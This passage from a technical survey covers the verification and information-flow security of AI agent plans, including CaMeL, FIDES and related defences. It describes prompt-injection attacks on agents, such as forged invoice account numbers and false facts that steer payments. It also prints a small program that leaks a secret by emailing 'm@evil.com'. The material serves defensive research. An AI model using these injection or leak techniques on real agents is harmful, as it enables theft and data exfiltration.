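$$\forall f \notin \{\text{foo.txt}, \text{bar.txt}\}:\; f \in F' \Leftrightarrow f \in F.$$

The verifier can now find a counterexample, a folder in which notes.txt exists before the plan runs and not afterwards.

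The tool's frame condition is still needed to verify the correct plan, which deletes the two files by name. Without it, the verifier could not rule out that deleting foo.txt also removes notes.txt, so it would reject the correct plan too.

The verifier rejects "*.txt" even when the folder holds only the two files, because it has no information about the folder's contents. This false rejection is a minor problem, since the proposer can name the files instead.

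Listing everything that an action leaves unchanged can be tedious, a difficulty that McCarthy and Hayes named the frame problem in 1969. clauz3's *Background And Related Work* describes a way to avoid it. clauz3 checks agent-written Python programs, and its contracts restrict a program's effects instead of describing the state of the world. For example, a contract might allow at most one email, and only to Bob. The checker works from a complete list of the program's tracked effects, so a tracked effect that isn't on the list can't happen.

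### Carrying a condition backwards

To check a plan against a contract, a checker can start from the goal and work out what must hold before each step. Suppose a company wants the agent to pay less than $10,000 in total. With amounts in cents, the goal is `total < 1000000`. This part of the plan handles one invoice:

```
if inv.supplier in approved and inv.amount < 50000:
    pay(inv)
    total = total + inv.amount
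```

The checker begins at the last line:

1. The last line adds the amount to `total`. For the goal to hold afterwards, `total + inv.amount < 1000000` must hold before it.
2. The payment doesn't change `total` or the amount, according to its frame condition, so the same condition must hold before the payment. The checker adds the payment's precondition, that the invoice is unpaid and the supplier approved.
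3. The branch has two outcomes. If its test succeeds, everything from step 2 must hold. If the test fails, nothing changes, so `total < 1000000` must already hold.

Let $g$ be the test, $t$ the total and $a$ the amount. The condition before the branch is

$$(g \Rightarrow \text{unpaid} \wedge \text{approved} \wedge t + a < 1{,}000{,}000) \;\wedge\; (\neg g \Rightarrow t < 1{,}000{,}000).$$

The test ensures that the supplier is approved. Without the supplier test, the checker would have to find an earlier step that established approval, or reject the plan. The test also limits the amount to 49,999 cents, so a total of at most 950,000 before the branch is low enough. Earlier steps must establish that the total is within that limit and that the invoice is unpaid.

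*Soteria* applies the same kind of reasoning forwards. At every point in the plan, it keeps a formula for the facts established so far. A tool call adds its postcondition, a branch adds its condition, and where two routes meet, the checker joins their formulas with "or". Before each call, the formula must imply the tool's precondition. Soteria also rejects a plan if some step could never run, or if a run could get stuck with no permitted next step.

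Contracts also let the checker reuse its work. Soteria verifies a standard procedure, such as a cancellation, once and then treats it as a single tool with its own contract. On airline tasks with GPT-5.4-mini, this raised the share of plans that passed the check within the retry limit from 38 of 60 to 65 of 68.

Soteria's executor can deviate from the plan, so the proof alone helped only a little. In a test with the same model and tasks, the proof raised the share of runs without a violation from 74% to 80%, and only the runtime monitor brought it to 100%.

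### Why a loop needs an invariant

The full plan repeats these lines for every invoice in the inbox. If a checker works backwards from the goal through a loop of unknown length, it needs a separate condition for each possible number of passes, and that number has no limit. Runtime Verification's *Formally Verifying Loops* describes the same difficulty for forward reasoning. When a checker can't tell whether a loop will continue, it has to follow both the exit and another pass, and the paths split again after that pass.

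An invariant covers every pass with one statement. Let $k$ be the number of invoices the plan has processed. Each payment is at most 49,999 cents, so a suitable invariant is

$$t \leq 49{,}999\,k.$$

The checker tests it in three steps:

1. Before the loop, $t$ and $k$ are both zero, so the invariant holds.
2. Each pass raises $k$ by one and $t$ by at most 49,999, so the invariant still holds after the pass.
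3. After $n$ invoices, the invariant gives $t \leq 49{,}999\,n$. The checker tests whether this implies the goal.

For step 2, according to course notes from the University of Washington, the checker discards the value of every variable the loop body changes and keeps only the constraints the invariant places on them. Checking the body once then covers every pass. An invariant that is too weak leads to a false rejection. For example, $t \leq 50{,}000\,k$ is also true, but after twenty invoices it allows a total of exactly $10,000, which is one cent too much.

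Even with the better invariant, step 3 succeeds only if there are at most 20 invoices. Twenty-one invoices for $499.99 each come to $10,499.79. A static checker can't determine how many invoices the inbox holds, so it has to reject the plan.

The proposer can fix the plan by making it stop before the first payment if it finds more than 20 invoices, or by making it test before each payment whether the new total would stay below $10,000. With the second fix, the simpler invariant $t < 1{,}000{,}000$ holds for an inbox of any size, but some qualifying invoices may go unpaid.

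The payment tool also requires that each invoice be unpaid, so the invariant must include "every remaining invoice is unpaid". This holds at the start if the search tool's postcondition guarantees a list of unpaid invoices without duplicates. It continues to hold because the payment tool's frame condition rules out paying one invoice changing the status of the others.

Proving that the reported total is correct requires the invariant mentioned earlier, that the total equals the sum of the payments so far. Erkok, in *Documentation.SBV.Examples.ProofTools.Sum*, uses an invariant in the same way to prove that a small loop correctly adds the whole numbers up to $n$.

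Checkers that find such proofs automatically have more trouble with sums. clauz3 can check a loop over a database result of unknown length by examining the body for one arbitrary row, but its *symbolic iteration* page lists running totals and sums over such rows as unsupported. Its bill payment example needs neither because it pays a single bill, and the checker proves that no branch pays more than the $500 limit. *Summing Up Smart Transitions*, by Elad, Rain and colleagues, treats sums of account balances in digital currencies as a verification challenge in their own right.

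### Solvers and proof assistants

Soteria runs its checks in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier. Like NuSMV, the verifier uses a solver to search for a counterexample, such as the 21 invoices. If the solver runs out of time, a sound checker must reject the plan.

A proof assistant, such as Lean, checks each step of a proof that someone else supplies. Proof-carrying code, the idea of shipping a program together with a proof, dates from the 1990s. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), an article based on a talk by Meijer, applies this idea to agents. In its example, a plan reads a file and reports the file's character count. A short Lean proof shows that the plan deletes nothing, whatever the file contains. No such proof exists for a plan with a deletion step.

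The proof doesn't show that the plan keeps the file confidential, or that the executor won't delete files while carrying out a "read" step. For some goals, nobody can write the contract. Meijer's example is a promise that a model's answers will be safe, which can't be written as a contract because "safe text" has no formal definition.

### Lean4Agent

Wang, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Lean4Agent*, apply contracts to workflows in which a language model performs the steps, such as "find the cause of this bug". Each step has an English instruction and a list of the variables it reads and writes. The system has three layers:

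1. Lean checks the structure, for instance that no step reads a variable before an earlier step has produced it.
2. A language model writes a precondition and a postcondition for each step, based on its instruction. Lean then checks that earlier steps establish every precondition.
3. After a run, Lean, ordinary Python code and a model judge test whether each step met its postcondition. This helps to locate the step that failed.

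The second layer assumes that if a step's precondition holds, the model can produce a result that meets the postcondition. Lean therefore proves that the steps fit together but doesn't prove that the model performs any of them correctly. In one faulty workflow, the instructions referred to earlier findings, but each step ran without access to the previous conversation.

Wang and colleagues tested whether passing the second layer predicts success. Claude Opus 4.6 wrote the workflows, and the researchers randomly picked three that passed and three that failed. Five other models then ran them on 50 hard software bugs from SWE-bench Verified and on 100 questions about AI research papers.

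| Benchmark | Success, passing workflows | Success, failing workflows | Difference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Software bugs | 58.27% | 43.47% | 14.80 points |
| Questions about papers | 36.60% | 27.53% | 9.07 points |

The average difference is 11.94 points, but each group has only three workflows, so one unusually good or bad workflow could account for much of it. Some of the benefit may also come from design advice built into the rules. Of 40 workflows for the paper questions, 21 failed, but only eight still failed when the researchers removed the rules about the workflow as a whole. One of these rules requires the model to judge multiple-choice answers independently or all together, so that its verdict on one doesn't influence the next. This is sensible advice, but it goes beyond checking that each step has the information it needs.

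### VeriGuard

*VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) verifies a guard that approves or blocks each action, instead of verifying the plan. The user states a rule in English, such as "never pay an unapproved supplier". A language model turns the rule into a Python function and writes the function's contract. The system asks the user about ambiguities and runs automatically generated tests. Then Nagini, a verifier for Python, tries to prove that the function meets its contract. If the proof fails, the model receives the error and revises its work.

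During execution, a language model extracts the function's inputs from the agent's data, and the function returns a verdict. Miculicich and colleagues compared this guard with a simpler one, a language model that evaluated each action directly. Both reduced attack success to 0% on the Agent Security Bench, a set of attacks on agents.

| Model | Attack success, no defence | Task success, model as guard | Task success, VeriGuard |
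|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 51.9% | 40.2% | 63.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 52.1% | 51.5% | 67.3% |
| GPT-4.1 | 63.7% | 44.6% | 57.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 49.9% | 68.3% | 85.1% |

VeriGuard's agents completed more tasks, but this experiment provides little evidence for the value of the proof. When the researchers added VeriGuard's components one at a time, the attack success rate fell to 0% before they added formal verification. Task success also depended a lot on what the system did after blocking an action. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, the task success rate was 44.6% when the system only withheld the tool's result, and 63.3% when it also told the agent which rule it had broken and asked for a new plan.

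The proof covers the function but not the model that extracts its inputs, and it can't show that the contract captures the user's rule. On Mind2Web-SC, which tests rules about who may do what on websites, VeriGuard with GPT-4o missed 1% of the forbidden actions, and about 9% of its denials were wrong.

### Who writes the contracts

In most of these systems, a language model drafts the contracts and people are supposed to find the mistakes. Soteria's developers compared each policy with the draft clause by clause. This took a few hours for each of three benchmarks, which needed 24, 33 and 41 rules. When they later audited the test results, they still found that the formulas misstated some rules and omitted others. Miculicich and colleagues likewise say that VeriGuard's guarantee depends on the user confirming that the constraints match the intention.

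clauz3 has the agent propose a contract for its own program, and the user approves the contract without having to read the code. The agent may propose a weak contract, but the weakness is visible. To leave email unrestricted, for example, it can state that it makes no guarantees about email. *Contract2Tool* (2026) has a model draft the preconditions and effects of each tool. The system then maps the draft onto a fixed vocabulary, which removes invented variables. A plausible but false effect would presumably get through.

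A false tool contract undermines every proof that relies on it. Comparing the contract with what the tool does can reveal the error. *ToolGate* (2026) tests the postcondition after every call and updates its record of the world only if the postcondition holds. Soteria stops the run when a postcondition fails, because its proof is no longer reliable.

Tests that check whether a tool call worked can also be wrong. *Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (2026) describes tests that only read data and return "true", "false" or "unknown". "Unknown" is useful when a bank takes a minute to show a transfer, because a test that returned "false" too early could lead the agent to pay a supplier again.

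Often there is no precise policy to translate. *Symbolic Guardrails for Domain-Specific Agents* reports that 85% of benchmarks relied on vague goals or common sense. Where policies were concrete, checks written as ordinary code or logic could enforce 74% of their requirements, often with little overhead.

### A shell tool can contain any program

Everything so far assumes that tools have useful contracts. Consider this plan:

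```
1  run_shell(script)  -> result
2  display(result)
```

A plan with two steps and no branches or loops belongs to the simplest kind of plan language. But if one step runs a script, that script can be any program, including one that never ends or deletes an inbox, and Rice's theorem applies to it. The expressiveness of a plan language therefore depends on its tools as much as on its grammar.

An accurate contract for `run_shell` can guarantee almost nothing, because the script it runs may change anything the shell can reach. The checker can therefore also prove less about the rest of the plan. If an earlier step found that a supplier was approved, the checker can't assume that the supplier is still approved after the script runs.

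A language model without tools is opaque in a different way. It changes nothing in the outside world, so it has a strong frame condition, but it has almost no postcondition. For example, it may return any number when asked for the amount on an invoice.

Weng, Wang and colleagues (2026) point out in *When Code Becomes an LLM Call* that a model call's postcondition holds only where the surrounding program checks it. They examined 496 places where 40 popular open-source agents call a model, and found that 48% of the model's outputs there either ran as code or helped decide what the program did next. Nobody saw 73% of those outputs before they took effect.

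For each place, one AI agent worked out which contract the task required, without seeing the code. Another extracted the checks in the code, and a third compared the two. Human reviewers checked every stage, either in full or on a sample. The code tested something both before and after the call in 82% of places, but met the whole expected contract in only 5.3%. Overall, the code did not meet 63% of the expected constraints or 72% of the expected postconditions. Deciding what a contract should require is partly subjective, so other analysts might get somewhat different figures.

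Programs often checked the form of a reply but not its meaning. STORM, a research agent, asks a model to answer "Yes." or "No." to whether a topic is appropriate. It rejects the topic only if the reply starts with "No", so a lowercase "no" counts as approval. An optional safety check in Google's Gemini CLI asks a model whether a tool call complies with a policy. If the request fails, or the reply is empty or unreadable, the program allows the tool call.

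### Limiting opaque steps

The most direct remedy is to offer narrower tools. If Meijer's deletion tool accepted only one exact file name, the proposer could not write the "*.txt" plan. But deleting a thousand log files would then need a loop or a thousand steps.

An allowlist keeps a general tool but limits it to certain commands, recipients or folders. Apache Magpie's *agent-guard* inspects every shell command before it runs, but filters that judge a command by its text can miss a differently written command that has the same effect as one they block.

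An output schema for a model call can require a positive whole number or a supplier from a list. The list rules out an invented supplier, but the model can still choose the wrong one. Weng and colleagues found 5,017 constraints in the agents' code, of which only 59 were requests for structured output and 114 tested whether a value was on a list or within a range.

A sandbox enforces a frame condition, or a limit on what a step can change, even when the checker cannot see into the step. If a script can write only to a temporary folder and has no network access, it cannot change the supplier list or the bank balance. The checker can then conclude that whatever was true of them before the script ran is still true afterward, without analysing the script.

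GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) describes GitHub Agentic Workflows, a product that combines several of these measures. It runs agents inside GitHub Actions, a service for automating software projects. By default, everything in an action shares the same level of trust, so a hijacked agent could obtain passwords or contact any server. The product therefore compiles each workflow into a GitHub Action with built-in restrictions. It also validates the workflow's structure in advance and gives the agent read-only permission.

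### Proving the framework instead of the plan

Each new plan needs a new check, but the software that executes plans changes less often. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) proves properties of that software. The proof assumes that the model may return any action of the permitted types, so it doesn't depend on how the model behaves. Moon and Varshney applied the method to PocketFlow, a small agent framework, using an interface with four action types. The policy limited the number of steps and allowed the agent to read files only inside its workspace and call only tools on an allowlist.

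The proof, which Dafny checks, compares a simple specification with a more detailed model of the framework. It shows that the two start in matching states, that each step of the detailed model matches a step of the specification, and that the safety of the specification's step carries over. If $s_i$ is the state before step $i$, $a_i$ the action the language model chooses, and $e_i$ the resulting event in the outside world, the policy $\Pi$ then holds at every step:

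$$\forall a_0, a_1, \dots \;\; \forall i:\; \Pi(s_i, a_i, e_i, s_{i+1}).$$

If the model chooses a forbidden action, the framework produces an event with no effect. A more capable model can't get around this through the same interface. But the guarantee holds only if every outside effect passes through the interface, and it doesn't cover bugs in Python or the operating system. Moon and Varshney also note that a general shell tool would defeat the purpose, because the proof could show only that the framework had called a permitted tool.

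Language models wrote both the specification and the proof. A model that sees the framework's code might write a specification that merely describes the code, faults included. Moon and Varshney therefore showed the model only the interface when it wrote the safety properties. Three tests then looked for poor specifications:

- Dafny had to accept the specification's syntax and types.
- The proof had to fail when the researchers' system removed most of its inductive invariant, which plays the same role as a loop invariant.
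- The proof had to fail when a model inserted a plausible error.

All specifications passed in four runs with two example workflows, and Dafny verified each path in 1.2 to 2.5 seconds. But the tests missed a serious gap in the template for safety properties, which had no field for some of the second workflow's effects. In a comparison run, the model was given the code, identified the mismatch and left the corresponding field empty. The property was then true only because it had nothing to restrict, just as "every recorded payment goes to an approved supplier" is true of a framework that never records payments.

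For the invoice task, a verified framework could guarantee that no plan, checked or unchecked, pays an unapproved supplier or spends $10,000 or more. Without a contract for the plan itself, it could not guarantee that the agent pays every qualifying invoice.

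## Values that arrive only at run time

Even with accurate contracts and a verified framework, the checker never sees some of the values a plan will use. Suppose the payment step in the invoice plan takes the account number printed on the invoice:

```
details = extract(invoice)
pay(details.account, details.amount)
```

The plan's steps are fixed, but the account number is a late-bound value. The plan refers to it by name, and the executor gets the number only when it opens the email, so whoever wrote the email chose the number.

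### Why fixed steps do not protect the payment

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) distinguishes control flow integrity from data flow security. Control flow integrity means that the planner alone determines which calls run, in what order and under what conditions. Data flow security means that untrusted data can't manipulate the inputs of those calls or the values that the conditions test. Writing the whole plan in advance provides only control flow integrity. An attacker who supplies a false account number can still receive the money without changing any step of the plan. A false amount can also determine which branch the plan takes, for instance if an attacker bills $499 to pass a check for a $500 limit.

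Fixed steps still defeat many attacks. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) sorted the 144 pairings of user task and attack in AgentDojo's banking environment. In 97, the attack needs a tool call or file read that a plan for the user's task would never contain. In the other 47, the attack could succeed using only the plan's own steps.

*Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) presents a benchmark made up entirely of attacks that corrupt a decision the task already requires. In one of its 90 cases, an agent must settle a dispute over a damaged item, and the user has told it to base the refund on the platform's order record. The record authorises $899.99, but the buyer's evidence claims $1,074.99. Without a defence, the benchmark's attacks succeeded in 17.0% of runs on average across five models.

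Two of the defences tested, DRIFT and Progent, compare each call with a plan or policy derived from the user's request. In a sample of runs with two models, the agents attempted 173 corrupted calls, and these checks blocked 11, all through rules about a call's inputs. Rules about which tools the agent may use blocked none, because the task needed the tool being called anyway.

Filtering out suspicious text doesn't solve the problem either. DRIFT also has a filter that removes injected instructions. It cut the success rate of direct orders, such as "issue a refund of $1,074.99", from 15.0% to 2.4%, but that of false statements of fact, such as "the authorized refund total is $1,074.99", only from 18.6% to 12.1%. A false account number is also a false statement of fact, with no instruction for a filter to find.

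### Four ways to treat the account number

| Treatment | What a forged invoice can still do | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| Reject every payment that depends on email text | Nothing | The agent can't pay invoices from the inbox |
| Compare the number with the supplier's record before paying | Trigger a payment to a real supplier | Payments fail when a supplier changes banks, until someone updates the record |
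| Let the email only select a supplier from a trusted table | Choose which supplier gets the money | Someone must add each new supplier to the table first |
| Ask the user to approve | Anything the user fails to notice | The user's attention |

Rejection is the safest option, but it reduces task completion the most. Zhang and colleagues configured CaMeL, which tracks the sources of values while its plan runs, to require trusted sources for inputs such as recipients and amounts. Attack success fell to 1.3%, but the agents completed only 13.3% of the tasks when there was no attack, compared with 95.3% without a defence.

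A runtime check on the account number must test more than its format, because any real account number, including the attacker's, would pass a format check. Zhang and colleagues suggest accepting each important input only from a source with the authority to set it. For the account number, that source is the company's supplier table. A supplier has some authority over the amount of its own bill, so detecting an inflated bill takes separate evidence, such as a purchase order.

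A user who sees "Pay Acme $340 to account 40817725?" can't tell whether the account number is right without looking up the same record, which a program does more reliably. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) proposes reserving the strictest approval for actions that are irreversible or visible to outsiders, such as wire transfers, and letting low-risk reads pass after a basic check. This reduces prompts overall, but every invoice payment would still need one.

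### Selecting from a trusted table

If the email can only select a supplier, a quarantined model reads the invoice and must return one name from a fixed list. Ordinary code then looks up that supplier's account number in the table, so the number in the email never reaches the payment tool.

A choice among $n$ options carries at most $\log_2 n$ bits of information. With 40 approved suppliers, each invoice can therefore convey at most

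$$\log_2 40 \approx 5.3 \text{ bits}$$

through the choice of supplier. A free choice of ten-digit account number would carry about 33 bits. The list should also include "none of these", which raises the limit only slightly, to $\log_2 41 \approx 5.4$ bits.

The limit applies to each invoice, so twenty invoices can carry about 106 bits. The amount gives an attacker about 15.6 more bits of influence per invoice, since there are 49,999 possible amounts under $500 in whole cents. A single bit can determine whether a $499 payment happens, so a low number of bits doesn't mean that little is at stake. The money is protected because all 40 accounts belong to approved suppliers.

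*Better Privilege Separation for Agents by Restricting Data Types* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) turns this idea into a general design in which one agent reads untrusted text and another chooses actions. The reading agent may pass on only whole numbers, decimal numbers, true-or-false values, and choices from a list written by the developer. None of these can contain an instruction. Free text stays hidden from the acting agent, though a program may insert it into a finished message.

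They tested this on three tasks:

- **Shopping:** The reading agent turns each product review into two numbers, for how strongly it supports the product and how relevant it is. The acting agent uses the median of each, which works if most reviews are honest.
- **Scheduling:** The reading agent turns an email conversation into a list of possible time slots.
- **Bug fixing:** The reading agent turns a bug report into a file number and some line numbers.

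| Task | Success, undefended | Success, restricted types | Attack success, undefended | Attack success, restricted types |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Scheduling | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | 49.7% | 14.6% | 94.3% | 0% |

The method did not reduce performance on tasks where a few numbers or time slots captured what the agent needed. It failed badly at bug fixing, because line numbers show where a bug is but not what the program should have done.

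Restricted types protect the acting agent from instructions but not from false data. In an example from Jacob and colleagues, someone misleads a stock-trading agent with a flood of negative posts. An account number is a whole number, so the type rule alone would accept a false one. The invoice agent therefore needs the narrower type, a choice from the supplier table.

### CaMeL

In April 2023, the developer Simon Willison described an assistant built from two language models. A privileged model plans and calls tools, while a quarantined model handles all untrusted text. The privileged model receives only a name for each value the quarantined model produces. *Twin Agent* (2026) explains that ordinary code replaces the name with the value when the action runs.

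CaMeL adds code generation and checks on data flow. Later papers describe its operation as follows:

1. The privileged model receives the user's request and writes a complete program in a restricted version of Python, before any tool runs.
2. An interpreter runs the program. When the program needs information from untrusted text, it calls the quarantined model, which must return data in a stated format.
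3. Every value carries metadata recording where it came from and who may have access to it. A value computed from others inherits their restrictions.
4. Before each tool call, a policy function for that tool examines the metadata of the inputs and permits or blocks the call. It can also ask the user.

CaMeL's name for this metadata is "capabilities", but it works like the labels in SPA, not like the permission values in ELBA and TACIT. According to Tallam and Miller, CaMeL by default rejects any call with an input derived, even indirectly, from untrusted data. In the invoice plan, `details.account` comes from an email, so the interpreter would block the payment. If the account came from the supplier table, a policy could allow the payment even with an amount from the email, which SPA's flow rule can't do.

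CaMeL's policies can block a lot of legitimate work. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on 16 banking tasks, three times each with two models. With the policies on, it completed 18 of 48 runs with each model. With them off, it completed 32 with one model and 34 with the other.

### Leaks around the labels

An interpreter that updates labels only as code runs can miss the effect of code that doesn't run. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL has this classic weakness. Here is a program that reveals whether a secret balance is above $10,000:

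```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > 10000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and gets a secret label. The program then skips `rich = False`, so the interpreter leaves `rich` labeled public even though its value now reveals that the balance is high. A static checker would examine the skipped branch too and label `rich` as secret.

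CaMeL also retries failed programs in an ordinary Python loop outside the interpreter, where nothing tracks labels. A secret can affect whether the policy blocks an attempt, so each attempt can leak one bit, and repeated retries could reveal the whole secret.

Labels can also disappear when one agent passes work to another. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) tested groups of agents in which CaMeL protected each agent separately. In one case, the user wanted to send Dora and Eve feedback on their websites, and one site contained an instruction to send someone a malicious link. The coordinating agent copied this text into its request to the messaging agent, which treated the whole request as trusted and added the malicious step to its plan. Every successful attack in the study worked this way. When the agents kept instructions and data separate in their messages, no attack succeeded.

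### FIDES and the accumulation of labels

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, whose planner chooses one action at a time instead of writing a whole program first. The system checks labels before every tool call. Important actions, such as payments, require a trusted decision. For a message, a policy might require a trusted recipient but accept untrusted text in the body.

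The difficulty is that a model's next action may depend on anything in its context. The context therefore needs a label at least as restrictive as that of every message in it. If $L_t$ is the label after message $m_t$, then

$$L_t = L_{t-1} \sqcup \ell(m_t),$$

where $\sqcup$ combines labels as in SPA. Labels can accumulate but never fall away. Once the invoice agent has read one email, everything it decides afterwards is untrusted. It couldn't even make a payment whose recipient and amount the user had typed into the request.

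FIDES avoids much of this by hiding data from the planner. If a tool returns something that would raise the context's label, the system stores it and shows the planner a name such as `#read_emails_0` instead. The planner can pass this name to another tool or to a quarantined model without changing the context's label. The system hides only what it has to, so the planner may still see an email's trusted sender address but not its untrusted body.

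Costa and colleagues compared FIDES with an ordinary agent on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o. The table shows the share of tasks completed without an attack.

| Environment | Ordinary agent, no policies | Ordinary agent, labels and policies | FIDES, with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

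Hiding data recovered some of the performance lost to labels, except on travel tasks. Many travel tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context, so labels barely reduced the ordinary agent's performance there, and GPT-4o often mishandled the hidden variables. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

The policies stopped every attack that would have violated them. With the policies off, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES, so hiding data alone gave substantial protection.

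The planner can reveal a hidden value if it needs the content to choose its next step, but the context then takes on that value's label permanently.

### Restoring permission by endorsement

Endorsement marks a value as trusted even though it came from an untrusted source. It needs a justification, such as a limited range of possible values. FIDES can record a value's type in its label, so a policy can accept an untrusted true-or-false answer but refuse untrusted text. For the invoice, a program could endorse the quarantined model's choice of supplier after confirming that the name is in the table. Costa and colleagues left this feature out of their AgentDojo tests because few of the tasks needed it.

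The user can also endorse data. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an email listing ten tasks, each of which requires a protected tool. If the user endorses the email, the agent can make all ten calls after a single interruption, whereas without that endorsement the user has to approve each call once the agent has read the email.

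Their agent, Prudentia, extends FIDES with this option. It also tells the planner which labels and policies apply, and requires the planner to explain why it needs to reveal hidden data before doing so. The main measure is the number of approvals an agent would need across all the AgentDojo tasks it completes.

| Model | Ordinary agent | Ordinary agent with labels | FIDES | Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|
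| o3-mini | 48.2 | 32.4 | 18.8 | About 17 |
| o4-mini | – | – | 36.8 | 19.2 |

With o4-mini, Prudentia needed 17.6 fewer approvals than FIDES, a reduction of nearly half. It also completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% compared with 75.7%), which may explain a little of the reduction. With o3-mini, it needed only about two fewer approvals, but it completed 59.1% of tasks without any approval, compared with 50.1% for FIDES and 24.3% for the ordinary agent.

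The experiment assumes that users approve every legitimate request and stop every attack; no real users answered the prompts. Kolluri and colleagues note that frequent prompts can cause confirmation fatigue, in which people approve without reading, so fewer prompts might improve each decision. But a mistaken endorsement can do more damage than mistakenly approving one payment, because endorsing a forged list of invoices exposes every payment on it.

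### What the LLMbda calculus proves

Neither CaMeL nor FIDES has a proof that covers every program an agent might write and every way that data might influence it. FIDES's formal guarantee covers secrets that flow directly from one place to another, but not what an observer could infer from the agent's choice of steps. CaMeL has no comparable proof.

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language, to fill this gap. Programs can send prompts to a language model, run code that the model writes, and copy or clear a conversation. A programmer can therefore implement a quarantined model in a few lines of code that ask a question in a fresh conversation. Every value and every conversation has a label. If a program uses a secret to decide whether to change a public conversation, the interpreter stops the program, which prevents the kind of leak found in CaMeL.

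The main theorem is about two runs of the same program that start with different untrusted data, such as a genuine account number in one and an attacker's in the other. If the language model always gave the same reply to the same conversation and both runs finished, all results labelled trusted would be identical. A payment tool that accepts only trusted inputs would therefore pay the same account both times.

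Real models reply at random, so the theorem concerns probabilities. Let $\mu_0(q)$ and $\mu_1(q)$ be the probabilities that the two runs finish with trusted results $q$. Each set of probabilities may add up to less than one, because some runs never finish or stop at a failed check. Garby and colleagues prove that a third set, $\omega$, always exists with

$$\mu_0(q) \le \omega(q), \qquad \mu_1(q) \le \omega(q), \qquad \sum_q \omega(q) \le 1.$$

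If both runs always finish, this forces $\mu_0$ and $\mu_1$ to be equal, so untrusted data has no effect on trusted results. Otherwise, if the runs fail to finish with probabilities $d_0$ and $d_1$, the difference is limited to

$$\frac{1}{2}\sum_q |\mu_0(q) - \mu_1(q)| \le \frac{d_0 + d_1}{2}.$$

If one run gets stuck 10% of the time and the other 20%, the difference is at most 0.15. Changing a secret can affect public results only within the same limit.

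The theorem doesn't protect the integrity of a value once a program has endorsed it. A second theorem shows that endorsement can't leak secrets, whatever the attacker puts in the untrusted data. Lean has checked both proofs, and they apply to the same interpreter that calls the language model. Both guarantees depend on developers to label data sources correctly and to put checks in the sensitive tools.

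Garby and colleagues also built Randori, an agent in LLMbda, and tested it on AgentDojo's banking tasks. The model that writes the plan may include endorsements, but only before it sees any outside data. In the 48 runs without an attack, Randori with GPT-5.2 completed 36, twice as many as CaMeL with its policies on. However, Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, so the comparison isn't quite equal. Disabling endorsement reduced completed runs from 36 to 30 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another.

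Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacked runs succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described in it, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The plan had endorsed whatever the file contained, so the proof no longer covered the payment details. Disabling endorsement blocks this attack but also blocks the legitimate payment.

### Plans that stop halfway

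A static checker rejects a plan before the agent pays any invoices. If a runtime check fails on the third invoice, the agent has already paid the first two, and the user may never receive the total.

If the agent starts again, it could pay the first two invoices a second time unless the payment tool records what it has paid. Garby and colleagues point out that an agent that gets stuck during a live run can repeat its side effects this way.

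Sometimes the system can skip only the blocked call. In the AgentDojo tests, FIDES reported the violation to the planner and let it continue. This works for paying invoices, because one forged invoice is no reason to leave the others unpaid. It works less well for actions that depend on each other, such as booking a flight and a hotel for the same trip.

A plan can reduce the risk by having the agent read all the invoices, select every supplier from the table and check every amount before it makes the first payment. If one of these steps fails, the agent can ask the user before anything irreversible has happened. But a bank can still decline the third transfer after accepting the first two.

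Rehearsal also helps with some errors. Randori first runs its program in a simulated environment and corrects it until it works, then runs it on the real accounts. The rehearsal treats every tool result as trusted, so it doesn't reveal where a label check will fail. A plan that passed rehearsal can still stop partway through the live run when it tries to use an untrusted account number.

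## Plans that are revised during execution

Suppose one of the invoices carries a notice that the supplier now accepts payment only through its web portal, which requires the customer to log in. The plan so far pays by bank transfer and has no step for using a portal.

A proposer that foresaw the problem could have written a branch for it:

```
if inv.method == "portal":
    note(inv, "asks for payment through a portal")
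else:
    pay(inv)
```

The notice then determines which branch runs, but the checker has already examined both. If the proposer did not foresee the notice, the agent can pay this invoice only by adding steps after reading the email, such as opening the portal, logging in and fetching a one-time code from the inbox. No checker has examined those steps, and the sender of the email influenced which ones the agent chose. An attacker could send the same notice with a link to a fake login page.

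### How many tasks need new steps

Piet, Chow and colleagues (2026) argue in *Position* that web agents should write a complete program before they look at a website. To find out how often this is possible, they examined 860 WebArena tasks and asked whether someone could write the program for each one using only the user's request and a description of the website's functions.

| What the task needs | Example | WebArena tasks |
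|---|---|---|
| A fixed program | Put the best headphones under $200 in the cart | 699 (81%) |
| A fixed program that calls a quarantined model | Summarise the reviews of the best-rated headphones | 161 (19%) |
| New steps during execution | Read my emails and do everything they ask | 0 |

Six people made these judgements by labelling the tasks by hand and settling disagreements by discussion, and no agent attempted any of the tasks. They also assumed that every website offered a complete and well-documented set of functions for programs to call, which real sites often lack. Postmill, the forum software in WebArena, offers 16 such functions, which are enough for only 33% of its 129 tasks.

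A program written in advance can also fail where a more flexible agent would recover. In one example from Piet and colleagues, a search for "COVID location tracker" finds nothing because the project's description lacks the word "tracker". A ReAct agent could then try a broader search, but a fixed program does so only if its author thought to include that step.

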